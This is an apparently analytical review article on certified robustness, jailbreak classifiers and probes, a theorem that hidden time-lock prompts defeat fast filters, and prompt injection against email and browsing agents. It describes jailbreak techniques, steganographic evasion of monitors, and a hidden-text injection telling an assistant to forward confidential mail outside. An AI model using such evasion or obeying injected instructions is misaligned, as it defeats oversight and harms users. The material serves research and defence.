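The formula works because the noise is spread widely compared with a small change to the image. If an attacker shifts the image by a distance *d*, the noisy copies also shift by *d*, but the old and new clouds of copies still overlap heavily. In the worst case, the region where the classifier errs lies directly in the direction of the shift, and the top label's probability falls from Φ(1.28) to Φ(1.28 − d/σ). A change of size 0.3 can lower it from 90% to no lower than 75%. A change of size 0.64 can lower it to 50%, at which point the runner-up can tie with it.

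The certificate applies only to the result of the vote, so the operator has to run the vote on every image. Noise of 0.5 is severe on a scale from 0 to 1, and a classifier that cannot recognise objects through it will get few certificates. Some recent versions first remove noise from each copy with a diffusion model, the type of network behind many image generators.

Since nobody can run the classifier on every possible noisy copy, the program must estimate the probabilities from a sample. Suppose the allowed chance of error is 0.1%. If 1,000 copies all get the same label, the lower bound on *p*₁ is 0.001^(1/1000), or about 0.993. With σ = 0.5, that limits the radius to 1.23, however robust the classifier is. If 10,000 copies all get the same label, the limit rises to 1.60. Hu and colleagues report that the method usually takes thousands to tens of thousands of runs per image, and that most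 evaluations have therefore covered at most 1,000 images.

They also regard an error rate of even 0.1% as unacceptable where security is critical. That objection seems weaker than the one about computation, because the defender adds the noise and the limit holds for any image an attacker picks. If all copies agree, lowering the limit from one error in a thousand to one in a million also requires only twice as many copies for the same radius. However, the operator has to consider repeated attempts, because an attacker who resubmits an image gets a new draw of the noise each time.

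Smoothing research commonly uses radius 1, about seven times the 36/255 common for Lipschitz networks. Cullen and colleagues write that Lipschitz methods can be ten times faster but often give smaller certificates. LipNeXt's reported gains are over other Lipschitz networks, so they do not show that it outperforms smoothing at radius 1.

### Certified training and unfinished checks

Verifiers such as α,β-CROWN can certify images with the same branch-and-bound search that they use on the aircraft networks. Certified training makes this easier by including bounds on the network's output in the training objective. Ladner and colleagues describe a benchmark from the 2026 verification competition, proposed by Konstantin Kaulen, with six networks trained this way. In this benchmark, the radius limits the change to each colour value separately. CIFAR-10 contains small photographs in ten classes,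 and TinyImageNet contains somewhat larger ones in 200.

| Images | Largest change per value | Network | Accuracy | Certified accuracy | Unfinished checks |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| CIFAR-10 | 2/255 | standard | 83.54% | 66.04% | 6.58% |
| CIFAR-10 | 2/255 | wide | 85.37% | 60.28% | 14.33% |
| CIFAR-10 | 8/255 | standard | 57.19% | 35.49% | 1.34% |
| CIFAR-10 | 8/255 | wide | 57.74% | 34.60% | 1.32% |
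| TinyImageNet | 1/255 | standard | 41.21% | 27.81% | 2.36% |
| TinyImageNet | 1/255 | wide | 41.89% | 28.35% | 4.01% |

Kaulen ran α,β-CROWN on 10,000 test images per network. Of the 60,000 checks, 2,994 were still unfinished after 1,000 seconds. Together, those used almost 35 days of computing time. For the competition, he selected 60 checks of varying difficulty, including 18 of the unfinished ones. The best verifier solved 38 of the 60.

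When some checks are left unfinished, a proof and a test can give quite different figures for the same network. For the wide network at 2/255, the verifier proved that 60.28% of the images were safe and reached no answer on another 14.33%. A test that counted only successful attacks as failures would put the network's robust accuracy at 74.6%. The true figure lies between the two, so the wide network may well be more robust than the standard one, despite its lower certified accuracy.

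These results and LipNeXt's use different measures of change but can be roughly compared. A CIFAR-10 image has 3,072 values, so changing each by the same amount gives a Euclidean distance of about 55 times that amount (the square root of 3,072). A Euclidean certificate of radius 108/255 therefore covers every change of up to 1.95 steps per value, almost the 2 steps in the table. At that radius, LipNeXt, trained with extra generated images, has a certified accuracy of 55.8%, ten points below the standard network in the table. Its ordinary accuracy is 92.7%, nine points above that network's. Its certificates also cover more changes, including a large change to one value when the others stay almost the same.

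### Why certificates have been hard to scale

Loose bounds were once the main obstacle for Lipschitz networks. Orthogonal layers have removed much of that obstacle by restricting the network's design. Mangal and colleagues note that ordinary attention, the mechanism transformers use to relate parts of an input, has no Lipschitz bound. LipNeXt does not use attention, but language models are built on it.

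Better bounds do not restore the accuracy that networks lose when developers train them for certification. LipNeXt labels 57.0% of ImageNet images correctly when trained for the small radius and only 41.0% when trained for the large one. Mangal and colleagues argue that this loss is not inevitable, provided that images with different labels always lie at least 2ε apart. For two labels, A and B, a short argument shows why. Define

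f(x) = ½ × (distance from x to the nearest B − distance from x to the nearest A).

Each distance changes by no more than *x* does, so *f* has *K* = 1. For any image of type A, the second distance is 0 and the first is at least 2ε, so the margin is at least ε. Every image therefore gets the right label and a certificate of radius ε. But computing *f* requires knowing every image that could occur, so a network has to approximate it from a limited sample. Mangal and colleagues acknowledge that such a function may be hard to learn and may require a larger network. LipNeXt improves steadily but slowly as its size increases, which is consistent with that expectation.

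These methods differ in when they need the most computation. A Lipschitz network needs it in training. One training pass through ImageNet took the larger LipNeXt almost 18 minutes on a machine with eight H100 processors, while each certificate needs only one run of the network. Smoothing needs little or no special training, but it takes thousands of runs for each certificate. These runs are independent, so an operator with many processors can finish them quickly, though the total computation stays the same. A verifier that splits cases may take a few seconds on one image and more than 1,000 seconds on the next, so it is poorly suited to a service that has to answer immediately.

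Even when the bounds are exact, a Euclidean certificate of a given radius gives weaker protection against changes spread across the whole image as the number of input values grows. For an image with *d* values, a certificate of radius *r* covers changes of up to r/√d to every value at once, as follows from a theorem in the paper by Cullen and colleagues. The value of √d is 55 for CIFAR-10 and 388 for an image of 224 by 224 pixels, so the same radius covers uniform changes only one-seventh as large in the larger image. A developer who cares about such changes can certify against them directly, as in Kaulen's benchmark, but the verifier then has to bound the effect of changing every input value at once.

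### Whether certificates amount to security

Cullen and colleagues argue that certified robustness does not yet imply security. Researchers compute certificates around clean images whose correct labels are known, but a deployed system computes them around images that an attacker may already have altered. Suppose an attacker makes a change of size 0.8 to a picture of a stop sign, the network classifies it as a speed limit sign, and the certificate has radius 0.3. The certificate is correct, because every image within 0.3 of the altered picture gets the same label, but that label is wrong. An operator therefore cannot use a certificate to distinguish clean images from attacked ones. Cullen and colleagues add the extreme case of a classifier that gives every image the same label, which is useless even though it can certify every image.

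The best reply to the stop sign case is a theorem that Mangal and colleagues had published two years earlier. The theorem assumes that the attacker can change an image by at most ε and that the system accepts an answer only if the answer has a certificate of radius ε. The original image then lies within ε of the image received, inside the certified region, so the attack did not change the label. The theorem does not apply to the stop sign example, because the change there was larger than the certified radius.

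Cullen and colleagues accept this reasoning when the attacker is known to be limited to changes no larger than ε, but add that the label may still be wrong for other reasons. The dispute is therefore more about whether anything imposes that limit than about the mathematics. Nothing imposes it on a service that accepts uploads, because the operator never sees the original image and cannot measure how far the upload differs from it.

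An attacker may also prefer a different kind of change, such as a rotation. Mangal and colleagues reply that resistance to tiny changes is a minimum requirement, because a network that fails under changes nobody can see is unfit for dangerous work, even if it withstands other kinds. They doubt that anyone can formally specify when two images mean the same thing. If a second network judged the similarity, an attacker could try to fool both networks at once.

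Some wider classes of change can be described precisely enough for a proof. A proof about rotations, for example, can bound the angle. So far such proofs can be very narrow. One benchmark in the 2026 competition covers camera movements on the order of a hundredth of a millimetre.

Cullen and colleagues also warn that certificates can help attackers, who can use a published radius to limit their search to changes outside it. They recommend showing certificates only to people with trusted access. No attack exists within the certified radius, so publishing it helps attackers only with changes that the certificate never covered. Mangal and colleagues acknowledge that if a system rejects uncertified images, an attacker can make it refuse legitimate work by altering images so that they fail the check.

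Refusals would be frequent even without an attacker. If LipNeXt gave only ImageNet answers with a certificate of radius 36/255, it would classify 41.2% of the test images correctly and refuse or misclassify the rest. Mangal and colleagues suggest passing uncertified cases to a person, which could work for a few images a day but hardly for a large service.

The last worry in *Position* is that words such as "guaranteed" may lead the people who buy and run these systems to neglect other protection, a possible result that Cullen and colleagues call "security theater". They grant that partial protection is better than none but expect complacency to outweigh the benefit. Their case rests on plausibility and a comparison with privacy technology, and they call for research into how users understand such claims. Mangal and colleagues concede that few practitioners have adopted certified defences,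 although they consider the research worthwhile. A fair label for LipNeXt on ImageNet would state the radius, the measure of change and the 41.2%, and few buyers would mistake that for complete protection.

### Certificates for text

In 2026, certificates for language models mostly concern classification. *CertMoE* (Wang, Gao and colleagues, 2026) certifies that a model's label stays the same if an attacker replaces up to *d* words. The models it covers classify sentences as positive or negative, or sort news into four topics. The method adapts smoothing to text. It hides a random 20% of the words, runs the model to get a label, repeats this many times and takes a vote.

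CertMoE is designed for mixture-of-experts models, in which a router sends each piece of text through a few of many sub-networks, called experts. Small changes to a text often change which experts the router chooses. CertMoE first certifies that the chosen experts stay within a somewhat larger pool, then certifies the model's vote when the model is restricted to that pool. The certified number of words is the smaller of the two results.

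Wang and colleagues tested certificates by attacking them, using 100 texts from each dataset. With two existing methods, the attacks broke between 33% and 39% of the certificates for sentiment. CertMoE lowered this to between 0% and 12%, but certified far fewer texts. With one model, the share certified fell from 94% to 38%. In the worst setting for news topics, attacks still broke 17% of CertMoE's certificates. The method allows a 10% chance of error, and a statistical test suggests that the excess is unlikely to be due to chance (p = 0.03).

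Wang and colleagues blame the failures of the older methods on the changing experts. That may not be the whole explanation, since smoothing proofs do not usually depend on how a model computes its answer. Another possible weak point is a term in the condition for a certificate:

lead of the top label > 2γΔ.

Δ is the probability that at least one replaced word remains visible, and γ is the probability that the model gives a particular label when that happens. With 20% of the words hidden and one word replaced, Δ is about 0.8. The most cautious choice, γ = 1, would then require a lead of more than 1.6, which is impossible because the lead is a difference between two probabilities and cannot exceed 1. Every certificate therefore depends on a smaller value of γ, which the program estimates from samples. It makes this estimate without knowing the attacker's text, so the estimate may be wrong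 for that text.

The sentence classifiers in the verification competition can be verified without sampling. A separate language model turns each sentence into 30 numbers, and a small network classifies those numbers. The developers generated variants of a sentence, including paraphrases, treated each variant's 30 numbers as a point, and found the smallest box containing all the points. A verifier can prove that the small network gives every point in the box the same label. But the proof does not cover the language model, and a paraphrase that the developers did not generate may fall outside the box.

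None of these properties describes a jailbreak, an input that gets a model to give help it is meant to refuse. A bound on changed words requires an original text for comparison, but a user attempting a jailbreak writes the whole message. The user can put a forbidden request into a story, translate it, spread it over several turns, or replace every word while keeping the meaning. Some jailbreaks add gibberish to the request, which changes the length of the text, whereas CertMoE counts replacements between texts of equal length. Certificates based on edit distance can handle insertions, but they also cover only a limited number of edits.

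The output is a further obstacle, because a chatbot can express the same dangerous advice in countless ways. No statement about its output is as precise as "the label stays the same" is for a sentiment classifier with two possible labels. A developer could instead certify a filter that labels incoming messages as allowed or forbidden. But if the filter mistakes a jailbreak for a harmless message, that wrong label can also be certified, as it was for the altered stop sign.

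## Chatbots: classifiers that screen for dangerous requests

Companies put filters around their chatbots to catch dangerous requests, but these filters come without provable guarantees. They are usually classifiers, smaller AI systems that check the user's messages, the model's answers or both. Developers judge them mainly by how long skilled attackers take to get past them. Anthropic, which makes the Claude models, has published a detailed account of one such system, Constitutional Classifiers, which is meant to stop the models from helping with chemical, biological, radiological and nuclear weapons.

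The attacker here is the user, unlike in prompt injection, where the user is the victim. The attack succeeds only if the user gets an answer good enough to act on.

### Why "give no dangerous help" resists specification

Attackers and defenders in computer security do much of the same work. In 2026, Anthropic published a list of what the classifiers on its model Claude Fable 5 should block. The classifiers should always block help with ransomware and allow a programmer to fix a known flaw. Writing an exploit, a program that takes advantage of a flaw, falls between these cases. Criminals write exploits, and so do the testers companies hire to attack their own systems. According to Anthropic, the difference is who is doing the work and who authorised it. The text of a request can at most include the user's own claims about this, so no formula applied to the text can establish who the user is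 or whether the work is authorised.

The right answer can also change over time. Anthropic gives the example of Log4Shell, a serious software flaw from 2021. An attacker who tricked a model into finding it in December of that year, when no other tool could, would have gained a dangerous advantage. The same output would give an attacker no advantage today, because every scanner detects the flaw.

The danger of an answer about weapons depends partly on whether its instructions would work, and finding out may require a laboratory. Researchers therefore use a substitute measure. *Constitutional Classifiers++* (Cunningham, Wei and colleagues, 2026) used eight forbidden questions about such weapons. For each question, language models listed the points a useful answer would contain, then checked how many of them an attacker's answer included. An answer counted as harmful if it scored at least half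 as high as one from a model without safeguards. This gives testers a consistent measure, but a proof based on it would only show how other language models grade answers.

### The 2025 version and its weaknesses

Anthropic introduced Constitutional Classifiers in February 2025. The "constitution" is a set of plain-language rules about what is allowed and forbidden, which Anthropic used to generate artificial training examples. One classifier checked the user's message and another checked the model's answer as the model generated it. The system increased computation by 23% and refused 0.38% of real user traffic. Cunningham and colleagues acknowledge that both the added computation and the refusals limited its practical use.

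Their further tests exposed two weaknesses. Some testers broke a request into harmless-looking pieces and spread them through a longer text, so the first classifier did not recognise it. Others got the model to answer in disguised language, which the second classifier could not interpret without access to the question.

Such disguises also make the model less capable. On a set of difficult science questions, Claude Opus 4 answered 74.2% correctly under normal conditions, but only 49% under one of these attacks and 32.3% under another. An attacker who needs expert help may therefore get poor advice. But the gap between the two attacks suggests that some disguises reduce capability much less than others, and Cunningham and colleagues expect that attackers could find better ones.

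### Judging the answer together with the question

Their first change was to replace the two classifiers with a single "exchange classifier". It reads the user's message, then checks the answer against that message in small batches as the model writes it. A sentence that seems to be about cooking may look dangerous next to the question it answers. A hidden request also tends to become visible once the model starts putting the pieces together in its reply.

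The exchange classifier made the safeguards use 50% more computation, because a larger model now had to read the answers. To reduce this, the researchers put a classifier that needs less computation in front of it. This first classifier reads every exchange and passes about a tenth of them to the larger one, and only the larger one can refuse. A false alarm at the first stage therefore wastes a little computation but does not bother the user, so the first stage can have a fairly low threshold for flagging exchanges.

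The first stage still uses most of the compute in this arrangement. Suppose running the larger classifier on one exchange takes 1 unit of compute. The smaller classifier takes about a third of a unit and runs on every exchange. The larger one runs on a tenth of the traffic, which adds 0.1 units per exchange on average. The total is 0.43 units, and the smaller classifier uses 77% of it. To save much more, the developers needed a first stage that used almost no compute.

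### Probes that read the model's internal activity

The solution was to reuse work that the chatbot had already done. A language model processes text in tokens, which are words or parts of words. For each token, every layer of the network produces a list of numbers called activations. A linear probe takes these numbers, multiplies each by a fixed weight and adds up the results:

z = w · ψ + b

where ψ stands for the activations, and *w* and *b* are numbers learned from examples. A high value of *z* means that the exchange looks harmful. For a model the size of Google's Gemma 3 27B, this takes about 377,000 arithmetic operations per token. Running even a small separate model with 4 billion parameters takes about 8 billion, or some 21,000 times as many.

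Training a probe is difficult because each example has one label for the whole exchange, but the probe must estimate the probability of harm at every token, before the rest of the answer exists. If two answers open with the same harmless paragraph and only one later becomes dangerous, ordinary training would push the probe towards a 50% probability of harm throughout that paragraph.

Cunningham and colleagues therefore weight each token's error by how harmful the probe thinks the exchange is at that point. Token *t* gets the weight

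exp(z_t) / (exp(z₁) + exp(z₂) + …),

where each *z* is an average over the last 16 tokens. If an exchange had only two positions, with scores of −3 and 3, the first would get 0.25% of the weight and the second 99.75%. The probe can thus give a harmless opening a low score at almost no cost, even if the exchange turns harmful later. But a confident alarm in a harmless exchange carries a heavy penalty, which makes sense because in use a single alarm can cut off the rest of the answer. The averaging prevents one odd token from setting it off.

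The researchers tried the probe on about 7,000 exchanges from testers' earlier attacks. When it used activations from every layer, about 1.4% of the attacks succeeded. The probe did almost as well as a separate classifier built from Claude Haiku 4.5, one of Anthropic's smaller models, but it raised more false alarms on harmless scientific requests. Combining the two worked better than using either alone, because their mistakes overlapped less than those of two separate classifiers.

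In the final system, the probe watches every exchange and sends suspicious ones to the Haiku-based classifier. The system then combines their scores:

final score = 0.55 × probe + 0.45 × classifier.

On real traffic, the probe forwarded about 5.5% of exchanges. The same calculation as before gives an average of about 0.055 units of compute per exchange, roughly an eighth of the earlier 0.43.

### What 1,736 hours of attacks established

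Cunningham and colleagues had testers attack each of the four designs, and classed an attack as high-risk if it drew harmful answers to more than five of the eight questions.

| Design | Relative cost | Attempts | High-risk attacks | Attacks that worked on all eight questions | Real traffic refused |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Separate input and output classifiers | 100 | 695,000 | 13 | 4 | 0.073% |
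| Exchange classifier | 150 | 226,000 | 2 | 1 | 0.038% |
| Two-stage classifiers | 27.8 | 569,000 | 5 | 0 | 0.036% |
| Probe and classifier | 3.5 | 198,000 | 1 | 0 | 0.050% |

Testers spent an estimated 1,736 hours on the final system. The one high-risk attack took 30 hours to find, and no attack drew answers to all eight questions that were at least half as detailed as an unprotected model's. The 40-fold reduction in compute is relative to the exchange classifier, which uses the most compute of the four. The reduction relative to the older design is about 29-fold.

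Most of the drop in refusals from 0.38% to 0.05% did not require the probe. The newer figure comes from a month of trial use on traffic to Claude Sonnet 4.5, but when the researchers rebuilt the older design and reset its threshold, its refusal rate was only 0.073%. The final system refuses slightly more than the two designs before it. The probe mainly reduced the amount of computation needed.

The attack counts alone also don't establish that the final system is more robust. If the first and last designs were equally hard to break and all attempts were independent, a split at least as favourable to the new design as 13 against 1 would occur about 15% of the time. The attempts were not independent, since one tester may make thousands of similar ones, and the researchers changed the questions and rewards between rounds. The reasons for the redesign are more persuasive, because the exchange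 classifier addresses weaknesses that testers had used.

A failed search gives a lower bound on the average time similar testers would need to succeed. Suppose they find universal jailbreaks, attacks that work across a whole range of forbidden requests, at a constant average rate. Finding none in 1,736 hours would then imply, with 95% confidence, an average of at least 580 hours of work per jailbreak. This bound applies only to people of similar skill who use similar methods against the same version of the system, not to someone who thinks of a new approach or automates the search.

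Testers in the bounty programme, which paid for successful attacks, made 569,000 attempts against the two-stage design and found no attack that worked on all eight questions. Experts outside the programme later found universal jailbreaks, using automated tools and considerable effort, as Cunningham and colleagues report in a footnote. The final system's clean result comes from the same kind of programme, so it does not rule out universal jailbreaks.

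### What government testers found

The UK AI Security Institute, a government body, attacks the safeguards of leading AI companies to test them. Its *Frontier AI Trends Report* (December 2025) states that the institute's experts found universal jailbreaks in every system they tested. The answers they obtained were nearly as accurate as those of a similarly capable model without safeguards.

The same report describes substantial progress. In tests of two models released six months apart, the experts needed 10 minutes to get past the first model's safeguards against biological misuse and more than seven hours for the second, a 40-fold increase. This is partly because the first model was still vulnerable to a published attack, while the second required a new one. A company can achieve some of that improvement by defending against published attacks.

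Protection was also uneven. According to *State of Jailbreaks* (Davies, 2025), a talk by a member of the UK AI Security Institute, jailbreaking took about five hours for biological misuse and ten minutes for other harmful content. Models whose weights anyone can download were about 15 times easier to break. Their users can switch off any separate classifier, and the developer cannot repair copies already in circulation. More capable models were not reliably safer. In data from a public attack competition, differences in capability accounted for only about 10% of the variation in robustness. The institute attributes most of the differences to the effort that companies put into their defences.

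In February 2026, the UK AI Security Institute announced an automated technique that generates universal jailbreaks against the best-defended systems. In April, OpenAI reported that the institute had broken GPT-5.5's safeguards against malicious hacking. The attack took six hours of expert work and succeeded on every malicious request OpenAI supplied for the test. OpenAI then changed the safeguards, but a configuration problem prevented the institute from checking whether the final version worked.

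OpenAI adds that the launch version blocked all the serious jailbreaks that other outside testers had found and verified, which shows that the company fixed the holes it knew about. For its later model GPT-5.6, OpenAI used more than 700,000 graphics-processor hours to search automatically for universal jailbreaks. Such a search covers far more variations than people can try by hand, but its results still depend on the kinds of attack the program can generate.

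A safeguard that takes seven hours to break instead of ten minutes still provides no guarantee, but it helps a company reduce misuse because fewer people will spend a working day on an attack. The institute expects that a novice would need much longer than its experts. OpenAI may also restrict or ban accounts that look dangerous. Much of the benefit of the longer time disappears if someone publishes a working attack before the company has blocked it.

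The UK AI Security Institute also argues that strong safeguards on today's leading AI systems can delay the point at which a dangerous ability becomes widely available, giving governments and others time to prepare. The delay is temporary because, as AI gets cheaper, more developers will be able to build models with that ability, and some of those models will have weak protection. An imperfect filter can provide this delay if it deters enough attackers for long enough.

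### The cost of false refusals

At 10 million exchanges a day, a refusal rate of 0.05% means 5,000 refusals a day, and the 2025 rate of 0.38% would have meant 38,000. Some of these refusals are justified, but probably only a small minority. If one exchange in a million were a real attempt to get help with a weapon, there would be ten such attempts a day, and at least 4,990 of the 5,000 refusals would be mistakes.

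The average refusal rate also doesn't show which users are refused most often. If 1% of exchanges concern biology or chemistry and all the refusals occur in those exchanges, a scientist would be refused in 5% of exchanges on those subjects, while most other users would never be refused.

When Anthropic released Claude Fable 5 in 2026, it was willing to accept many more false alarms because it judged that misuse in biology could be catastrophic. Anthropic later explained that the model was so capable in biology that the company launched it with almost all biology questions blocked and had a less capable model answer them instead. Understanding AI's *Anthropic's Fable is the most locked-down public model we've ever seen* reports that even "What is protein?" triggered the switch at first. The 0.05% figure measured on Claude Sonnet 4.5 therefore does not apply to Fable 5.

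Anthropic's classifiers for computer security block some requests that are probably harmless because they resemble dangerous ones. Anthropic calls these requests the "safety margin". A wider margin catches more attacks but also turns away more legitimate users. Anthropic made the margin wider for Fable 5 than for its earlier models.

Users who know that a safeguard has been triggered can at least rephrase their question or go elsewhere. Fable 5's safeguards for work on advanced language models were at first invisible. Anthropic later made them visible and apologised for having hidden them, according to Fortune (2026). The company also warned that users might see more false alarms while it refined the classifiers.

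Companies can block fewer legitimate requests by applying different rules to different users. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) describes a single model released in two forms. Claude Fable 5.1, for general use, has extra safeguards in areas such as biology and cybersecurity, while Claude Mythos 5.1 has a different level of protection. OpenAI gives security professionals wider access after verifying their identity. An identity check supplies some of the context missing from the text of a request, but the company must then trust approved users to be honest and keep their accounts secure.

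### A proof that some models cannot be filtered

Better training may make classifiers harder to fool and reduce false alarms. But *Computational Barriers to Filtering for AI Alignment* (Ball, Gluch and colleagues, 2026) proves that for some models, no amount of training can make a fast external filter reliable. Its main theorem concerns a filter with access only to the user's prompt, not to the model's internals.

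Let *G* be any source of harmless prompts with enough variety. If certain cryptographic puzzles exist, then there are a model *M′* and a second source of prompts, *G′*, such that

- prompts from *G′* can make *M′* produce harmful output, and
- no filter that runs significantly faster than *M′* can distinguish them from prompts from *G*.

A useful filter has to let the harmless prompts through, so it will let the harmful ones through as well.

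The proof relies on time-lock puzzles, which are quick to create but take a set amount of work to solve. The best-known kind starts with two large secret prime numbers, *p* and *q*, and their product *n*. The task is to take a number *r*, square it *t* times in a row, and find the remainder on division by *n*. As far as anyone knows, a person who has only *n* must do the squarings one after another, so extra processors do not help. The puzzle's creator, who knows *p* and *q*, can take a shortcut by first reducing the exponent 2ᵗ to its remainder on division by (p − 1)(q − 1).

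With *p* = 7, *q* = 11, *r* = 2 and *t* = 10, squaring *r* ten times and keeping only the remainder on division by 77 each time gives 4, 16, 25, 9, 4, 16, 25, 9, 4 and 16. The creator instead divides 2¹⁰ = 1024 by 6 × 10 = 60, which leaves 4, and computes 2⁴ = 16. This shortcut saves little work with such small numbers but an enormous amount when *n* has hundreds of digits and *t* is in the billions.

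The attacker in the proof creates a puzzle and uses its solution as the key to encrypt a forbidden request. Further processing makes the puzzle and the encrypted request look like a string of random digits to anyone without the time to solve the puzzle.

He then has to turn these digits into an ordinary-looking prompt. A language model writes by choosing each token at random, according to probabilities it calculates. The attacker runs the harmless source *G* in this way but uses his digits in place of random ones. For example, where "Can you" and "Could you" are equally likely, a 0 could select the first and a 1 the second. Since the digits look random, the prompt looks like any other from *G*.

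The model *M′* reverses the process. It works out the digits from the choice of words, solves the puzzle, decrypts the request and answers it. If it finds no hidden message, it responds to the prompt normally. The attacker does not need to share a secret with the model, so any user could carry out the attack.

Choices are rarely so evenly balanced. If one word has a probability of three-quarters, several combinations of digits lead to it, and the model cannot determine from that word alone which one the attacker used. Ball and colleagues solve this by using the unresolved part to choose later words, so that the model can eventually recover all the digits. The harmless source needs enough variety because a prompt with no choice of words cannot carry a message.

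The filter fails because it has less computing time than the model. The attacker sets *t* so that *M′* can finish the squarings but the filter cannot. A filter with as much time as *M′* could solve the puzzle and read the request. Filters are usually much smaller than the models they protect, since a filter of equal size would roughly double the cost. Ball and colleagues cite Meta's Llama Guard 4 filter, which has about 12 billion parameters, far fewer than the leading chatbots.

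*On the Impossibility of Separating Intelligence from Judgment* (Ball, Gluch and colleagues, 2025), an earlier version of the paper, also proves two results that do not require the filter to be weaker than the model. In one, the attacker and the model share a secret key. In the other, the model has a public key that anyone can use to encrypt a request. The filter then fails even if it has more computing time than the model, as long as it cannot break the encryption. These stronger results require a model designed to cooperate with attackers.

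A filter that edits prompts before passing them on will not necessarily scramble a hidden message. Ball and colleagues (2026) prove that the message can survive if it is hidden with a method for watermarking text that withstands the same kinds of edits.

### The separate result on outputs

A filter that reads answers has more information than one that reads only prompts. But Ball and colleagues prove that such a filter still fails in some cases, even if it sees both the prompt and the answer and has more computing time than the model. In these cases, the model hides a time-lock puzzle in its answers through its choice of words. The puzzle takes far too long for any practical filter to solve, so the filter cannot distinguish the harmful answers from harmless ones.

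The proof also defines harm to fit the model. An answer is harmful if the hidden puzzle contains a harmful message, and the judge of harm has far more computing time than the filter. Ball and colleagues describe this judge as the outside world, where the consequences of an answer eventually appear. They give the example of a business plan that cuts costs by subtly recommending the exclusion of certain clients. A reader might approve the plan and see the damage only later.

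The result is less relevant to instructions for making a weapon. Ball and colleagues point out that if harmful answers are easy to recognise, an output filter is easy to build. Someone who wants instructions must be able to read them, and if that takes little computation, a good filter may be able to read them too. The user could ask for an encrypted answer and decode it later, but the filter could then refuse answers it cannot read. The proof rules out that defence only for messages hidden in text that looks entirely normal.

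### How far the theorem reaches

The theorem shows that unfilterable models exist, but not that Claude or ChatGPT is one of them. *M′* searches every prompt for a hidden puzzle and acts on whatever it finds, and no developer would deliberately build a public chatbot to do that. Ball and colleagues concede in the 2025 version of the paper that this behaviour is contrived. But they argue that artificial-looking weaknesses have turned into real attacks before, citing the theft of more than $60 million from the cryptocurrency system Ethereum in 2016 through a flaw that had once seemed mainly theoretical.

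Their better argument concerns a regulator or customer who cannot inspect a model and may want a filter that works whatever the model contains. The theorem rules out a fast prompt filter of that kind, because the model might be *M′*. A developer who trained the model and can examine it is in a stronger position, although training a model does not reveal everything it has learned to do.

The experiments in the 2026 paper offer only limited support for the theory. Ball and colleagues tried 1,097 jailbreak prompts on two filters. Llama Guard 2 let through 34% of them, and ShieldGemma let through 79%. But Llama Guard 2 has 8 billion parameters, more than two of the three models it protected, which had 3 billion and 7 billion. Its errors with those two models cannot be due to its being smaller than they were.

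In a second experiment, closer to the idea of the proof, the researchers put the prompts into simple codes. The share that passed Llama Guard 2 rose to between 66% and 88%, depending on the code. ShieldGemma, which had missed most of the uncoded prompts, caught slightly more in one code and fewer in the others. These codes are easy to undo, so developers could train a filter to recognise them, but no training would help against a true time-lock puzzle. The UK AI Security Institute raises a similar concern that, in real systems, an attacker may converse with a capable model in a language or code that a weaker monitor does not understand.

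Anthropic's current system falls outside the main theorem for two reasons. It checks the answer as well as the prompt, so it may detect a hidden request once the model responds in plain language. It also reads the model's activations, and the theorem covers only filters without access to them. To answer a hidden request, *M′* must first decrypt it, so the decrypted text exists somewhere in its activations, which gives a probe something to detect. Whether the probe would succeed is an open question, because the theorem does not address this case and the probe was trained on ordinary jailbreaks.

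Ball and colleagues conclude that companies must invest at least as much in safety as in capability. This seems too strong, at least as a rule about computing power, because the probe draws on all the computation that the chatbot performs yet adds almost none of its own. But only someone with access to the model's internals can use a probe. Customers who reach the model over the internet usually see only text, and the same may be true of government auditors, so Ball and colleagues recommend that auditors get access to the weights.

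## Browsing agents: training and detection against prompt injection

In prompt injection, an attacker hides instructions in material that a model reads, to make it act against its user. Anthropic gives the example of a user who asks an AI assistant to read her recent emails and draft replies to any meeting requests. One email looks like an enquiry from a supplier but contains white text on a white background, which the assistant can read but she cannot see. The hidden text is an instruction to forward every email containing the word "confidential" to an outside address before drafting the replies. If the assistant follows it, the attacker has her confidential mail before she sees the first draft.

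A prompt injection attacker never has to deal with the assistant or its provider. Jailbreaking a chatbot usually requires an account, which the provider can monitor and close, but a prompt injection only requires sending an email, posting a hotel review or editing a web page. A single page can attack every agent that reads it. Anthropic considers these attacks especially dangerous for agents that can both read private data and act for the user, as email assistants are designed to do. *Defending Against Prompt Injection with DataFilter* (Wang, Chen and colleagues, 2025) lists several attacks that worked on real products. For example, instructions on a web page got Anthropic's computer-use agent to download and run malware, and instructions in public software bug reports got OpenAI's Operator to reveal a developer's private information.

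### Why the database remedy does not carry over

An agent's model receives the developer's instructions and the user's request, and responds with a tool call, such as "open the newest email". Ordinary software carries out the call and adds the result to the model's input. The model uses this longer input to produce its next call, repeating the loop until it gives a final answer. The supplier's email therefore ends up in the same sequence of tokens as the user's request. Developers can label the email as data, which David C of Britain's National Cyber Security Centre says can make attacks harder. But the labels are text too, and the model has learned only from examples how much weight to give them.

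A parameterised query keeps values separate from commands, but David C points out that a language model has no equivalent separation between instructions and data. It only predicts the next token from all the text before it. Training a model to favour its instructions, or highlighting which part of the text is data, adds a distinction that is not built into the underlying technology.

He suggests that developers think of the model as a "confused deputy", a security term for a program that an outsider can trick into using its permissions for the outsider's benefit. Developers can fix an ordinary confused deputy, but he calls language models "inherently confusable". He warns that if companies build AI into most of their applications without planning for this, a wave of breaches may follow, as happened with SQL injection.

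His argument does not prove that no remedy exists, and he says only that there is "a good chance" of never finding one. A model without a built-in boundary might still learn to respect one almost all the time. However, the tasks people give to agents create a further difficulty. A customer's name in a database query never has to work as a command, but a user may ask her assistant to deal with the to-do list a colleague has emailed her. The assistant then has to follow some instructions in the email and ignore others.

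*The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents* (Wang, Li and colleagues, 2026) calls such tasks context-dependent. It found that many defences do well on existing tests by suppressing what the agent reads, then fail on tasks where the agent needs that material. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) found that attacks succeed much more often when the user names no action and leaves the agent to do whatever the content says. So even a model that could perfectly distinguish the user's words from everyone else's would still have to work out which outside instructions the user meant it to follow.

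### Training, detectors and filters

One defence is to train the model itself. Anthropic puts injections into simulated web pages during training and rewards Claude for recognising them and refusing to comply. This protects every product that uses the model, with no extra work for the products' developers, but only a company that controls the model's weights can do it.

Such training can also have side effects. In two simulated tests, earlier versions of Claude Opus 4.5 misreported or left out something they had found. One version failed to mention a planted note about how to smuggle out a model's weights. Anthropic attributes both cases to its training against prompt injection. A model that learns to ignore suspicious text may fail to tell users about it, although they might want to know that someone has tried to attack them.

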